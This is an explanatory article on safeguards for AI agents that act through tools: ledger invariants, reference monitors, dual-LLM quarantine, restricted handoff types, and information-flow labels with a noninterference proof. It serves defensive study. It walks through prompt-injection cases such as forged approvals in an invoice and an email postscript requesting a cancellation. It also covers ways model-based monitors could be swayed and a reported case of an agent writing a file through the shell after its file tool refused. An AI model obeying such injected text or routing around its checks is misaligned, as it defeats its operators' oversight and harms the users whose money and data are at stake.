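# Runtime guarantees enforced on data structures rather than on model outputs

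## What it means to guarantee the data structure and not the model

Runtime guarantees on data structures are safeguards for AI agents, programs in which a language model takes actions as well as writing text. They apply to the records, messages and permissions through which an agent acts, and they make a forbidden action fail whatever the model has produced. For example, if a bank ledger rejects overdrafts, an auditor doesn't need to know who will request payments, or why, to know that the account will not go below zero. Operating-system designers spent five decades building protections of this kind. *Ring-0 by Default* (Li, Huang and colleagues, 2026) compared 116 operating-system mechanisms with their counterparts in agents and found 65 missing, most of them protections.

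A language model alone cannot overdraw an account. Given some text, it only computes a probability for each possible next fragment of text. Willison (2025), in *I think “agent” may finally have a widely enough agreed upon definition*, defines an agent as a language model that runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal. The software around the model, called the harness, passes the model its inputs and carries out its requests. Each request is a tool call that names a function and gives its arguments, such as `pay(invoice: 17, amount: 600)`. The harness runs the function, adds the result to the model's next input, and calls the model again. As Brooker points out in *Agent Safety is a Box*, all the agent's effects on the world pass through its tools.

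An outsider can influence the model through its inputs. The operator's instructions, the user's request, the output of a tool and the contents of a file all reach the model as text, and according to Li and colleagues the model cannot tell them apart. A supplier can therefore write "the finance director has approved double payment" in the small print of an invoice, and the model may act on it. When a model obeys text in the data it reads as an instruction, this is called prompt injection.

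Agents also cause trouble without an attacker. Brooker (2026) thinks the most common problem is their persistence. In *Music To Build Agents By*, he compares them to the enchanted broom in Goethe's poem "The Sorcerer's Apprentice", which keeps fetching water after the basin is full. An agent told to clear every outstanding invoice by Friday may treat an empty account as an obstacle to get around.

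### One rule in three places

Suppose a company's agent pays invoices from an account holding €1,000, under the rule "never pay more than the account holds". Two invoices arrive, for €600 and €700.

The easiest option is to write the rule in the prompt, the text that instructs the model. The rule then holds if the model takes account of it at every turn, uses the current balance, subtracts the €600 before it considers the €700, and gives the rule more weight than any instruction in an invoice. On long jobs, the rule must also remain in the model's limited input. A harness has to compress old parts of the conversation to make them fit, and standing rules can be lost when it does.

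The company can instead put the rule in a filter that reads the model's output and blocks bad payments before the harness makes them. Many production harnesses use a second language model for this, according to *Tether* (2026), a paper on a policy engine for agents that work in a terminal. The first model then no longer has to follow the rule, but the filter has to recognise every bad payment, however the agent words it or splits it up, and it needs an up-to-date balance. A filter that looked up the €1,000 balance once and checked each invoice separately would approve both.

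A filter built on a model has a further weakness, because it reads text that the agent wrote. Li and colleagues examined two such monitors, in the coding agents Claude Code and Codex CLI. Both correctly blocked the action in all ten trials in which the monitoring model's reply was missing or malformed. But both also read the text of the action under review, and Codex CLI's monitor read the agent's justification too and stored its verdict in a file the agent could write to. Li and colleagues did not try to persuade either monitor to approve a harmful action, so they identified a possible vulnerability but did not demonstrate an attack.

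The third place is the ledger, the program that records the balance and the only one with the credentials to instruct the bank. When asked to pay an amount *a* from a balance *b*, the ledger tests whether 0 < *a* ≤ *b*. If so, it sets the balance to *b* − *a* and sends the money. If not, it returns an error and changes nothing. The test and the subtraction form a single step, so no other payment can occur between them. The €600 payment goes through and leaves €400, so the request for €700 fails. It fails again if the model repeats it or argues for it. If the model splits the €700 into €400 and €300, the €400 goes through and the €300 fails.

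An invariant is a statement about a system's state that must be true after every step. Here the invariant is *b* ≥ 0. It holds at the start because the opening balance is not negative. If *b* ≥ 0 before a request, then either the ledger rejects the request and *b* doesn't change, or *a* ≤ *b* and the new balance *b* − *a* is at least zero. So the invariant holds after any number of requests, in any order and from any source.

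The test also needs its other half, 0 < *a*. Without it, the ledger would accept a "payment" of −€500 and raise the recorded balance above what the bank holds. Choosing an invariant that captures the rule is often harder than proving one, and here *b* ≥ 0 would stay true even though a later payment could spend money that does not exist.

The three designs also differ in their enforcement points and trusted bases. An enforcement point is the place in the software that refuses a request that would break a rule. The trusted base is all the hardware, software and configuration that must work correctly for a guarantee to hold. The prompt has no enforcement point, and its trusted base includes the model and, in effect, everything the model reads. The filter has an enforcement point, but if the filter is a model, that model is part of the trusted base. The ledger's trusted base consists of the comparison,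 the database, the machine and operating system underneath, the custody of the bank credentials and the accuracy of the opening balance. Any of these may fail, but the model is not part of the trusted base.

But the rule covers only what the ledger can express. The ledger records balances and amounts but not whether the company ever ordered the goods, so a forged invoice for €300 goes through just as a real one would, which defeats the rule's purpose even though the rule is satisfied. Forcing the model's output into a fixed schema does not help, because a schema can ensure that the amount is a number but not that it is the right number. The Agentic AI Foundation's *How to build reliable AI agent systems for production* makes the general point that a policy check cannot correct a decision that the agent based on context it should never have trusted.

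*Kairos* (2026), a paper on holding back an agent's actions until a monitor has validated them, attributes the difficulty of validation to the monitor's limited information. Whether an action is authorised often depends on where a piece of data came from, which the monitor can only approximate, and on what the user intended, which nobody can fully specify beforehand. A monitor that can only approve or reject actions must then err towards refusing legitimate work or letting attacks through.

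Adding rules widens the coverage, but only incrementally. *ConfGuard* (2026) describes a monitor for agents that schedule industrial maintenance, and identifies a deterministic policy outside the model as the dominant defence. Most such policies check where a value came from and which tool may receive it. ConfGuard's policy checks whether the value is physically plausible for the machine, and the paper claims that the two kinds of check reject entirely different calls.

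### The reference monitor

The conditions for trusting an enforcement point predate agents. The United States Air Force commissioned *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) to determine how people with different security clearances could safely share one computer. The study identified the hard case as a malicious user who has legitimate access to the system and can run his own programs on it. A model in a harness is in much the same position, because it has valid permissions and can issue any request the interface accepts.

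Anderson proposed the reference monitor. Every time a user's program tries to use data, a device or another program, the monitor checks the attempt against a list of what that user is allowed to do. Anderson set three requirements for the monitor.

- The mechanism must be tamper-proof, since a check that an attacker can alter is worth nothing.
- The system must always invoke it. If the check is switched off for some group of programs, those programs become part of the security apparatus and have to meet the same requirements.
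- It must be small enough for analysis and testing whose completeness people can assure. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study. Volume 2*, equates this with being capable of proof.

He showed how a real system could fail them. On the Honeywell 635, a hardware register kept each user's program inside its own area of memory, but most of the operating system ran with that check suspended, so the system did not always invoke it. Treating the operating system itself as the monitor would not have solved the problem, because nobody could completely check its 200,000 to 300,000 instructions.

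The invoice ledger's comparison easily meets the third requirement, but the ledger can still fail the other two. If the agent can write to the database table that stores the balance, it can credit itself with a million euros. If it can run shell commands and read a file containing the bank credentials, it can pay without going through the ledger. Coding agents already have gaps of this second kind. Li and colleagues asked Gemini CLI, Google's coding agent, to write a file outside the folder where its file tool can write. In all five runs the agent wrote the file through the shell, in four of them after the file tool had blocked the write.

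The same researchers graded common defences against Anderson's three criteria. Rules in the system prompt failed all three. Training a model to rank its operator's instructions above other text got partial credit for being hard to bypass and failed the other two. Hooks, pieces of code that intercept each tool call, passed the first two and got partial credit for verifiability. Operating-system sandboxes and policy engines with formal rules passed all three. These grades are judgements about types of mechanism, and the Gemini CLI result shows that a particular installation can fall well short of its type's grade.

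Anderson also listed the concept's assumptions: reliable identification of users, physical security, protected communications and working hardware. The ledger's trusted base includes all of these too.

### What happens when the model changes

A filter's accuracy is measured by running it on outputs that particular models produced under particular attacks and counting the errors. A new model may phrase its requests differently or find routes the old one never tried, and attackers adjust to the filter once they can probe it. The filter may remain as accurate under these changes, but the measurement doesn't guarantee that. The proof about the ledger, by contrast, covers every possible request, including those from models that do not exist yet.

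Even a highly accurate filter is also likely to miss something over many attempts. If a filter catches 99% of bad payments, and assuming for simplicity that each attempt is independent, the chance that at least one of 100 attempts gets through is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%. A real attacker would do better, because they can reuse a wording that has worked once.

Anderson had a similar complaint about the "tiger teams" that tested security by trying to break in. Their successes revealed flaws, but when a team failed, the only safe conclusion was that "the security state of the system is unknown".

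Li and colleagues tested whether an agent that saves a file will overwrite a change somebody else has made in the meantime. When a script issued the commands in place of the model, a write through the shell destroyed the other person's change in all three coding agents they examined. With a real model, the change survived in 99 of 99 valid runs, because the model reread the file first or only added to the end of it. A replacement model need not share these habits, but someone who saw only those 99 runs would conclude that the system itself protects concurrent edits.

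Better models can also undermine the ledger's guarantee, because it depends on the trusted base. A more capable agent is more likely to find a bug in the ledger or a forgotten copy of the credentials. The proof would still be valid, but one of its assumptions would be false.

### Safety as a contract, and as a box

Ng, Han and colleagues (2026), in *Agent Safety Should Be a Runtime Contract*, base a position about the whole field on this contrast. Most alignment research tries to make the model itself behave well through training, often by rewarding outputs that a learned scoring model rates highly. The score is a statistical approximation of what people want, and a strongly optimised model can exploit the difference. Training data are also finite, so a deployed agent may receive inputs from users and attackers that its training did not cover. Ng and colleagues accept that agents can game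 formal rules too, but argue that rule breaches are visible and quick to fix, whereas a model can exploit its reward without being noticed. This is a little too favourable to rules, because the ledger records no breach when a forged invoice is paid.

The proposed contract has a preventive side and an evidential side, both enforced by the harness. On the preventive side, the harness blocks dangerous actions before they happen. On the evidential side, it accepts a task as complete only if there is evidence that a deterministic program can check without trusting the model. The invoice agent could prove payment with a ledger entry, but not with the model's statement that it had paid.

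To support this, Ng and colleagues coded 52 publicly reported incidents from March 2016 to January 2026. They judged that a working harness would have fully prevented 40 and partly mitigated 11. They attributed the remaining one, involving Meta's game-playing system CICERO, mainly to the model's goals. The coding rests on their own view of what would have happened otherwise, and they present it as evidence of a recurring pattern, not as causal proof for each case. A bigger problem with citing the 40 in favour of rules on data structures is that Ng and colleagues count output filters and behavioural monitors as parts of the harness, alongside sandboxes and permission gates. The figure therefore does not separate mechanisms that work regardless of the model from those that depend on classifying its output correctly.

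Ng and colleagues apply the contract to an agent's effects, not its thinking. This is their reply to the objection that much of what people want from agents has no checkable standard. A short story needs no schema, but the call that emails it to someone does, with fields for the recipient, the body, the attachments and any prior approval. Where no standard exists, they would refer to a human any action that cannot safely be repeated.

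Brooker reaches a similar conclusion from engineering. People build agents because they are flexible enough to handle cases nobody planned for, but that flexibility makes it hard to establish what an agent will never do. He grants that training and careful prompting improve how often an agent succeeds and what it costs to run. For safety he wants a "box", a deterministic layer outside the agent that limits which tools it can call and what it can do with them. In the cloud version he describes, the network lets the agent send traffic only to a gateway, which checks every tool call against a policy. Brooker works on these products at Amazon Web Services, and he offers an argument and a design but no measurements.

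In his main example, which is close to the invoice case, no refund may exceed the original price and no order may receive more than one refund. With both rules in the box, a company can work out the most it could lose to refunds without worrying about the latest prompt injection. The sample policy he prints is weaker. It lets a named agent issue refunds of less than 500 but doesn't mention the original price or earlier refunds, so the agent could refund 499 on the same order a hundred times without violating the policy.

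## Restricting the data types that untrusted text can become

The ledger rejects a bad payment when the request arrives, but by then the supplier's small print has already reached the model with access to the payment tool. Some designers act earlier by keeping untrusted text away from that model and letting through only simple values, such as a number or a choice from a list. They rely on types, which describe the values a piece of data may take and the operations a program may perform on it. For example, data of the type "whole number from 0 to 10" can take only eleven values, so it cannot contain a sentence.

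### Two models and a controller

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed splitting an assistant between two language models. The privileged model takes the user's instructions and can call tools. The quarantined model has no tools and reads emails, web pages and anything else an outsider could have written. Willison assumes that the quarantined model may go rogue at any moment. The controller, which is ordinary software, acts as the harness between the two models.

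Suppose the user asks for a summary of the latest email.

1. The privileged model asks the controller to fetch the email and store it as `$VAR1`.
2. The controller does so, without showing the privileged model the text.
3. The privileged model asks for a summary of `$VAR1`.
4. The controller gives the email's text to the quarantined model and stores the reply as `$VAR2`.
5. The privileged model writes "Your latest email, summarized: $VAR2", and the controller fills in the summary on the user's screen.

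`$VAR1` and `$VAR2` are opaque variables, which the privileged model can pass on by name but cannot read. If the email contains an instruction to delete the inbox, only a model that cannot delete anything will read it.

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) formally describes what this achieves. An injection cannot add tool calls, but it can make the quarantined model's answer wrong, and the plan then uses that answer. In one example, the plan sends a reply drafted by the quarantined model, and an injection makes that model copy the user's notes into the draft. In an example from *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), an injected email cannot change the subject or body of the agent's message, but it can influence who receives it, because the quarantined model takes the recipient's address from that email. To catch either problem, the harness needs a label on the value that records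 where it came from or who may see it.

Willison called his own solution "pretty bad". The summary can still mislead the user, for instance with an instruction to paste encoded private data into a website. He also worried about complexity, because a single programming mistake that lets untrusted text reach the privileged model would undo the protection.

### Tasks that depend on the hidden text

The privileged model has to plan without access to the contents of its variables, which is impossible for some tasks. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025) gives the example of an assistant that must read three emails and create a calendar event if one of them asks for a meeting. The privileged model can fetch the emails and have the quarantined model extract a date. But it can't check whether any of the emails asks for a meeting, so it can't decide whether to create the event.

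The paper calls a task data independent if a single sequence of tool calls and final responses solves it for every possible value of the stored data. Forwarding three emails to a colleague is data independent because the same two calls work whatever the emails contain. The meeting task is not, because every solution creates an event if there is a request, and no solution does if there is none. A better model would not help, because it would still have no information about whether there is a request.

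How much this matters depends on the kind of work. The same paper classified the 97 user tasks in AgentDojo, a benchmark with four simulated environments. Data-dependent tasks made up 5% of the office tasks and 10% of the travel tasks, but 43.8% of the banking tasks and 42.9% of the Slack messaging tasks.

Willison made one exception, for a quarantined model that only sorts text into a fixed set of categories, because the controller can check that the output is exactly one of them before passing it on. *L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026) describes a reader for bug reports that works this way. A program fetches the report and gives it to a fresh model that has no access to the network or the project's files. The program asks the model whether the report describes a regression, a fault in something that used to work, and reduces the reply to "yes", "no" or "unclear". Any other reply,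 a failure or a timeout becomes "unclear". The agent that acts on the report receives only that word.

### Numbers and choices in place of text

Type-directed privilege separation, which its designers first posted in September 2025, extends Willison's exception from a single category to whole records. The quarantined agent converts untrusted text into a record called a handoff, whose fields may hold integers, floating-point numbers (numbers with a fractional part), booleans (true or false) and enumerations (choices from a list fixed by the developer). A field may also hold an array (a list of such values) if the array's length is limited. Without the limit, a long enough list of integers could encode a message to the agent, with each integer standing for a character.

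The designers' first test case is a shopping agent that searches WebShop, a simulated store with roughly 1.2 million products, for an item that fits the user's request. Anyone could have written the product reviews, so the privileged agent never reads them. Instead, the quarantined agent reads each review and returns two integers from 0 to 10, one for how strongly the review supports the product and one for how relevant the review is. The privileged agent takes the median of each score, notes the number of reviews, and then chooses its next action.

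Each score has 11 possible values, so a review can produce 11 × 11 = 121 different handoffs. A choice among *N* possibilities carries at most log₂ *N* bits of information, so the agent receives at most log₂ 121, or about 6.9, bits from a review of any length. That is slightly less than the seven bits that ASCII, a standard code for English text, uses for one character.

*Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) generalises the calculation. If *D* is the set of permitted values, the capacity of the boundary is log₂(|*D*| + 1) bits per message. The extra one is for rejection, which an attacker can use as another signal if they can cause it at will. The shopping case therefore has 122 outcomes, still about 6.9 bits. For the bug-report reader, Eisenach and colleagues count three outcomes, about 1.6 bits, because failures come back as "unclear". They add that the timing of the call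 must reveal nothing more.

These limits apply to each message, so the total grows with the number of messages. Fifty reviews could together carry about 346 bits, enough for 49 characters. The medians reduce this, provided that ordinary code computes them and shows the privileged model only the result. With an odd number of reviews, the model then sees one of 121 possible pairs of medians, plus the count.

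The medians also make it harder for a minority of reviewers to manipulate the scores. Suppose a product has five reviews, and the three honest ones get support scores of 7, 8 and 9. If an attacker wrote the other two and both score 0, the median is 7. If both score 10, the median is 9. Two fake reviews can therefore move the median only within the range of the honest scores, but an attacker who wrote three of the five could set it to anything. The median is reasonable protection against one dishonest reviewer, but it offers little in a shop where posting a review is free.

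The privileged agent also reads the rest of the item page directly, so the guarantee covers what reviewers write but not what a seller might put in the product description.

### Calendars and bug reports

In the second test case, an agent arranges a meeting by email. The quarantined agent reads the other person's emails and returns a list of suggested times, chosen from predefined slots, and an opaque description of the meeting. The privileged agent compares the times with the user's calendar and decides whether to reply or finish. Another model, isolated from the quarantined one, drafts any reply.

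Array lengths matter because a longer list of slots can carry more information. The test calendars have 63 one-hour slots, nine a day for seven days, so one slot carries about six bits and a list of ten carries about 60. If the harness sorts the list and removes duplicates, the list can carry at most 63 bits, whatever its length, because each slot is either in it or not.

The opaque description is a weak point. When the two sides agree on a time, the agent copies the description into the user's calendar, which the privileged agent can read. A later request could expose the privileged agent to the attacker's text unless the description stays opaque when the agent reads the calendar.

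The third test case is a coding agent that fixes bugs, and its handoff is the most elaborate. The quarantined agent reads the bug report, explores a copy of the code and returns:

- one of 52 bug categories, such as "off-by-one bug"
- one of three sizes of fix
- a list of code regions, each with a file number, a first and last line, and one of eight roles, such as "region suspected to contain the bug"

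A planner sees this handoff but not the bug report, and writes three possible plans in ordinary prose. Another model, which has read the report, compares the plans and returns only the number of the best one. The privileged agent then uses the handoff and the chosen plan to work on a clean copy of the code.

The designers attacked each agent with and without the defence. In the shopping test, they added a notice to one review claiming the product was a banned substance and ordering the agent to leave the page. In the calendar test, the other person asked for the user's whole week, including the event descriptions. In the coding test, the bug report asked for an unrelated extra file.

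| Agent | Model | Tasks completed, undefended | Tasks completed, defended | Attacks successful, undefended | Attacks successful, defended |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shopping (500 requests) | GPT-4o | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0.0% |
| Calendar (100 pairs of people) | GPT-4o | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0.0% |
| Bug fixing (180 bugs) | GPT-5.2 | 68.3% | 45.0% | 98.9% | 0.0% |

The defence did not measurably reduce performance in the shop or the calendar. The coding agent's success rate fell by 23.3 percentage points, which means it failed to fix about a third of the bugs it would otherwise have fixed. The designers attribute this to the benchmark's reliance on real bug reports, where the prose matters a great deal. That seems right, because a line range can show the agent where to look but not what the program should have done. They also needed considerable testing on 52 other bugs before settling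 on this handoff, so the method takes work for each new application.

The zeros in the last column are less informative than they look. The designers believe the design guarantees security, and they ran the attacks to verify it. All three attacks tried to give the acting agent an order. An attacker who knew about the handoff would instead tell the quarantined agent to score a good product 0 or to blame the wrong file, and none of the attacks tried this.

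### How the harness enforces the handoff

A developer specifies a handoff with a schema, a machine-readable list of its fields and their types. Prompting the model to follow the schema doesn't guarantee that it will, but constrained decoding enforces the schema as the model writes. At each step, the decoding software excludes any fragment of text that could not lead to a valid record, then uses the model's probabilities to choose among the rest. Where the schema permits only `true` or `false`, the model cannot start writing "Ignore the user", however high a probability it assigns to those words.

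OpenAI first converts each schema into a context-free grammar, a set of rules for which sequences are well formed, according to an employee quoted in Willison's *OpenAI structured outputs*. In *Structured outputs*, Anthropic guarantees field types and required fields by the same general method. Agents already use structured outputs for quarantined models. In *SPA* (2026), a security design for agents that keep data between requests, the quarantined model has no tools and must answer in a given schema. If it cannot complete the task, it is instructed to return a failure value from the schema, where there is one.

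The services enforce different parts of a schema, so a handoff that is safe with one provider may be unbounded with another. AWS supports enumerations but not minimum and maximum values, so a developer has to write "0 to 10" as a list of eleven numbers or check the range separately. Google's *Improving Structured Outputs in the Gemini API* announced support for both limits. Databricks' *Structured outputs* warns that its service does not enforce size limits on arrays. The OpenAI employee also described a rare failure in which a model gets stuck in a loop, printing technically valid output.

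Free text can also get past a schema. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Structured Outputs in the API*, a model can still refuse a request, and the refusal arrives as a separate string. If the harness forwards that string to the privileged model, the quarantined model can use it to send prose. A model that is allowed to add fields can also write a sentence as a field name, which AWS prevents by requiring schemas to forbid extra fields. AWS also accepts strings in the format of an email address or a web address, but a handoff should not treat these as safe types, because both can contain readable words chosen by the attacker.

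It is safest for the harness to parse the finished record itself, check every range and length, and discard anything that fails. The provider's decoder then improves reliability but is no longer part of the trusted base, which contains only the checking code and the code that decides which model sees which data.

### Can a number carry an instruction?

Type-directed privilege separation is claimed to eliminate the possibility of prompt injection through its data types. For small ranges and short lists, this is true in the sense that no sentence from the attacker can reach the privileged model. The claim becomes weaker as the types allow more values. A 64-bit integer can encode eight characters, enough for "PAY EVE!", and a 100-digit integer can encode about 41. A model would have to decode the number unprompted and then obey the text, which is improbable, but the method was meant to avoid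 relying on such judgements about the model. A range of 0 to 10 does avoid this, because it is too small to encode a sentence.

Numbers that point to text raise a different problem. In the bug-fixing handoff, the quarantined agent chooses a file and a range of lines, which the privileged agent then reads. If an outsider has planted an instruction in a comment or test file, the attacker's bug report can direct the privileged agent to that line. The handoff is safe only if all the text it can point to is safe, so the design needs a trustworthy copy of the code.

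The safety of an enumeration depends largely on what its choices mean. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* describes an agent, FIDES, whose quarantined model may choose from a list of tasks such as `schedule_meeting`, `out_of_office_reply` and `forward_email`. An attacker who controls that choice can't write an instruction but can select one. If the agent also took the forwarding address from the same email through an opaque variable, the attacker would control both the action and its target. The paper is more cautious than the designers of type-directed privilege separation. It says a boolean alone is unlikely to lead to a prompt injection, but leaves it to the policy whether such a value may influence important actions. Its experiments did not include constrained decoding, so they provide no evidence on how safe such values are.

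A value that carries no instruction can still be false. A quarantined model that has obeyed an injection can return a support score of 0 for an excellent product, and the record will pass every check. The designers exclude such deception from their threat model, the set of attacks they aim to stop. They consider it arguably distinct from prompt injection but accept that it can make the agent less useful. Eisenach and colleagues note the same limit in their three-word reader, which can still return a wrong "no".

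An injection that can only choose among permitted values may still harm the user. *Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (2026) examines a bill-paying agent that may pay only the user's known billers. This rule stops every injection that names an account off the list, but an injection can still cost the user money by having the agent pay a listed biller a second time.

The number of bits an attacker controls does not measure the damage they can do. If a single boolean decides whether to release a €300 payment, one false bit costs €300. But a small type gives the developer a short list of cases to examine. With 121 possible handoffs and everything else held constant, an attacker can choose among at most 121 inputs to the privileged agent, and a developer can run the agent on all of them, which is impossible with free text. These runs will show whether the answer "yes, the goods arrived" is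 enough to get a forged invoice paid. If it is, the developer will need a delivery record that the supplier cannot write to.

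## Labels that travel with data

A delivery record protects the invoice agent only if the harness can distinguish it from the supplier's own claim that the goods arrived. Both may be the single word "yes", so they have the same type and differ in who could have written them. To track this difference, information-flow control has the harness label each value with its origin or its permitted readers, and compute each new value's label from the labels of the values used to produce it. The harness can then allow or refuse a tool call based on the labels, regardless of the values' text.

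### Four labels and a rule for combining them

Dorothy Denning set out the mathematics in 1976. She arranged labels in a lattice, an ordered set in which any two labels have a lowest label above both. That label is called their join and written ⊔. The order is written ⊑, and *l* ⊑ *m* means that data labelled *l* may flow to a place that accepts data labelled *m*.

According to *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026), labels most commonly record integrity, meaning whether data is trusted, and confidentiality, meaning whether it is secret. With U for untrusted and S for secret, there are four labels:

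- {} for trusted, public data, such as the user's request
- {U} for untrusted, public data, such as a web page
- {S} for trusted, secret data, such as the company's bank balance
- {U, S} for data that is both, such as a stranger's private email

Data may flow from one label to another if the second contains all the marks of the first. The join of two labels is the union of their marks, so a sentence that combines the balance, {S}, with a supplier's text, {U}, gets {U, S}. "Untrusted" ranks above "trusted" because a place that accepts untrusted data can safely accept trusted data, but not vice versa.

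A label can also list people. If Ana, Ben and Carla may read one document, and Ben, Carla and David may read another, only Ben and Carla may read a text that draws on both. If the same lists named possible writers instead, the combined text's label would list all four people, because any of them could have influenced it.

Joins can add restrictions but never remove them, so labels tend to become more restrictive over time. Under the high-water mark, a scheme from 1969, checking a spelling in an unclassified dictionary while writing a secret report made the dictionary secret. Agents have the same problem, because a single web page can taint a whole conversation.

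### How a check refuses an email

*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) presents LLMbda, a small programming language for agents that attaches a label to every value. In one example, Alice asks her agent to send Bob a reminder about a meeting he mentioned in an email. An attacker posing as Bob has added a postscript to the email, asking for a cancellation instead. LLMbda's `send_email` function accepts a message only if the label of its subject and body may flow to {S}, so it accepts messages labelled {} or {S} and refuses those labelled {U} or {U, S}.

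1. Alice's request enters the conversation, which has the label {}.
2. The model asks for the email. The harness adds the text, and the conversation's label becomes {} ⊔ {U} = {U}.
3. The model asks to send a message with the subject "Meeting Cancellation". The harness can't tell which part of the conversation shaped this request, so the request takes the label of the whole conversation, {U}.
4. `send_email` tests whether {U} may flow to {S}. It may not, so the program stops and sends nothing.

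When Garby and colleagues ran such an agent on GPT-4o with a mail tool that lacked the check, the agent sent the cancellation. With the check, the agent is safe but useless, because an honest reminder written after reading the email would also be labelled {U}. The label records only where the text came from, which is the same for both messages.

The dual-LLM pattern avoids this. The privileged model writes a plan as program code before it reads the email, so the subject and body are fixed text with the label {} and pass the check. The recipient's address still comes from the email and is labelled {U}, but this version of `send_email` doesn't check the address. This version also lets a secret body go to anyone. Garby and colleagues mention a variant that sends secret text only to recipients on an approved list.

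### Noninterference and the branch that did not run

In 1982, Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer defined the property that such labels should guarantee. A system has noninterference if changing its protected inputs does not change what an observer without access can see. For a deterministic program *f*, this means that *x* ≈ *y* implies *f*(*x*) ≈ *f*(*y*), where ≈ means "looks the same to the observer". The definition also covers trust. If changing the untrusted inputs never changes an output labelled trusted, an attacker can't influence that output.

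Noninterference is a property of pairs of runs, so a monitor that watches one run at a time can miss a violation. In the textbook example, the variables `a` and `b` start out public and only the balance is secret.

```
a = true
b = true
if balance > 1000000 then a = false
if a then b = false
if b then email an outsider
```

The balance determines which instructions run, even though the program never copies it. This is called an implicit flow. Suppose that, to track such flows, a monitor marks a variable as secret whenever the program assigns to it inside a branch that depends on a secret.

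| | Balance above €1 million | Balance of €1 million or less |
|---|---|---|
| `a` after the third line | false, {S} | true, {} |
| `b` after the fourth line | true, {} | false, {} |
| Email | sent | not sent |

When the balance is high, `a` is false, so the program skips the assignment to `b`. The monitor can't mark a variable for an assignment that never runs, so `b` stays public and the email goes out. When the balance is low, `a` is still public, the assignment runs, and no email goes out. The outsider learns whether the balance exceeds €1 million, although the monitor handled every executed instruction correctly.

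J. S. Fenton described this leak in 1974. Garby and colleagues found it again in CaMeL, an agent system in which a privileged model writes a plan as code and an interpreter tracks labels while it runs the plan.

One remedy is to analyse both branches before the program runs. LLMbda instead uses a runtime rule called "no high upgrade". The interpreter stops the program as soon as code in a secret-dependent branch tries to change something public. In the example, a high balance would stop the program at the third line, before it could send the email. A smaller leak remains, because anyone who can see that the program stopped learns that the balance was high.

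### Conversations with labels

LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language built from functions. A labelled value has the form *l*:*v*, where *l* is the label and *v* the value. The conversation with the model also has a label, and four operations act on it:

- `send` adds a message to the conversation and joins the message's label to the conversation's
- `recv` draws a reply from the model and runs it as code under the conversation's label
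- `fork` runs part of the program on a copy of the conversation, then restores the original
- `clear` empties the conversation and removes the marks that its messages had added

The interpreter also keeps a program-counter label, which joins the labels of all the decisions that led to the current instruction. Every value the code produces has at least this label, so if a model has read an attacker's text and replies with a program, everything that program computes is untrusted.

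Developers can create a quarantined model in a few lines of code with `fork` and `clear`. The program forks the conversation, clears the copy, asks the copy its question about the email and returns the answer. The answer keeps the mark U, but the main conversation isn't marked. Developers can therefore choose where to isolate the model, whereas CaMeL and FIDES build the isolation into their architecture.

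LLMbda also has to stop the conversation from leaking a secret through a branch that didn't run. In one test, a program asked the model to remember that *x* was false, and was then to send a second message setting *x* to true only if a secret was true. The interpreter refused to send the second message because its presence in a public conversation would have depended on the secret.

### Endorsement

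An agent sometimes has to act on untrusted data, such as when it reads an email, chooses a category like "general", and uses that category as the subject of its reply. Endorsement is an explicit step that marks untrusted data as trusted, and in LLMbda it removes the mark U. It can't remove S, so endorsing a value labelled {U, S} gives {S}. The result also keeps the program-counter label, so endorsement has no effect in code generated from an attacker's text.

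This protection works only if the attacker's text still has its mark. If the program has already endorsed the text and then runs it as code, the code counts as trusted and can endorse other values. Garby and colleagues describe a stricter version that adds a third mark, E, to every endorsed value and prevents any value with that mark from being endorsed again.

Another version endorses only values from a fixed list of *n* choices, so the attacker controls at most log₂ *n* bits each time. The program has to endorse a copy of the untrusted value, check the copy against the list, and keep it only if it matches. If it compared the untrusted value with the list first, it would enter an untrusted branch, where endorsement has no effect. Garby and colleagues have not yet proved a formal bound for this version or characterised what the stricter one guarantees.

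### The noninterference theorem

A language model may answer the same question differently each time, so noninterference for an agent has to compare probabilities. Ideally, two starting states that look the same to an observer would produce every visible outcome with equal probability. LLMbda does not achieve this, because a secret can affect whether a check stops the program. Garby, Gordon and Sands prove a weaker property, termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference:

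*C*₀ ∼ₘ *C*₁ and *e*₀ ∼ₘ *e*₁ ⟹ ⟦*pc* ⊢ *C*₀, *e*₀⟧ₘ ⌣ ⟦*pc* ⊢ *C*₁, *e*₁⟧ₘ

Here *C*₀ and *C*₁ are conversations, *e*₀ and *e*₁ are programs together with their data, and *pc* is the program-counter label. The observer sees only data whose label may flow to *m*, and ∼ₘ means "looks the same to this observer". The double brackets stand for the probabilities of the final outcomes as the observer sees them. These may add up to less than 1, because some runs never produce a result.

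The symbol ⌣ means "compatible". Two sets of probabilities *μ* and *ν* are compatible if there is a third set, *ω*, that gives every outcome at least as much probability as both *μ* and *ν* do and adds up to no more than 1. In other words, the two could become identical if more of the unfinished runs finished.

For example, suppose a program answers "yes" or "no" with probability 0.5 each when the balance is low. When the balance is high, it answers "yes" with probability 0.5 and otherwise stops. The larger probability for each answer is 0.5, and the two add up to 1, so the cases are compatible. If the program instead answered "yes" with probability 0.9 and "no" with probability 0.1 when the balance was high, the larger probabilities would add up to 0.9 + 0.5 = 1.4. The theorem rules out a total above 1 for answers the observer may see.

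The theorem also limits the size of the leak. The statistical distance between the two cases, which is half the sum of the differences in probability, cannot exceed the average probability of not finishing. In the compatible example, both are 0.25. If the program always finishes, the two sets of probabilities are identical.

The proof uses a second way of running the program, in which the interpreter skips any computation once its label exceeds what the observer may see, and returns an empty record. This version never uses the hidden data, so it gives the same probabilities, *ω*, for both starting states. It also reaches each visible outcome at least as often as the real program does. Because *ω* sums to at most 1, the real program's probabilities for the two starting states must be compatible.

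The result covers every program in the language, including code the model writes during the run, and holds whether or not the model is honest. Endorsement weakens the protection of trusted data by design, but a second theorem shows that it doesn't weaken secrecy, whatever untrusted inputs the attacker chooses and whatever the program endorses.

### What the Lean proof covers

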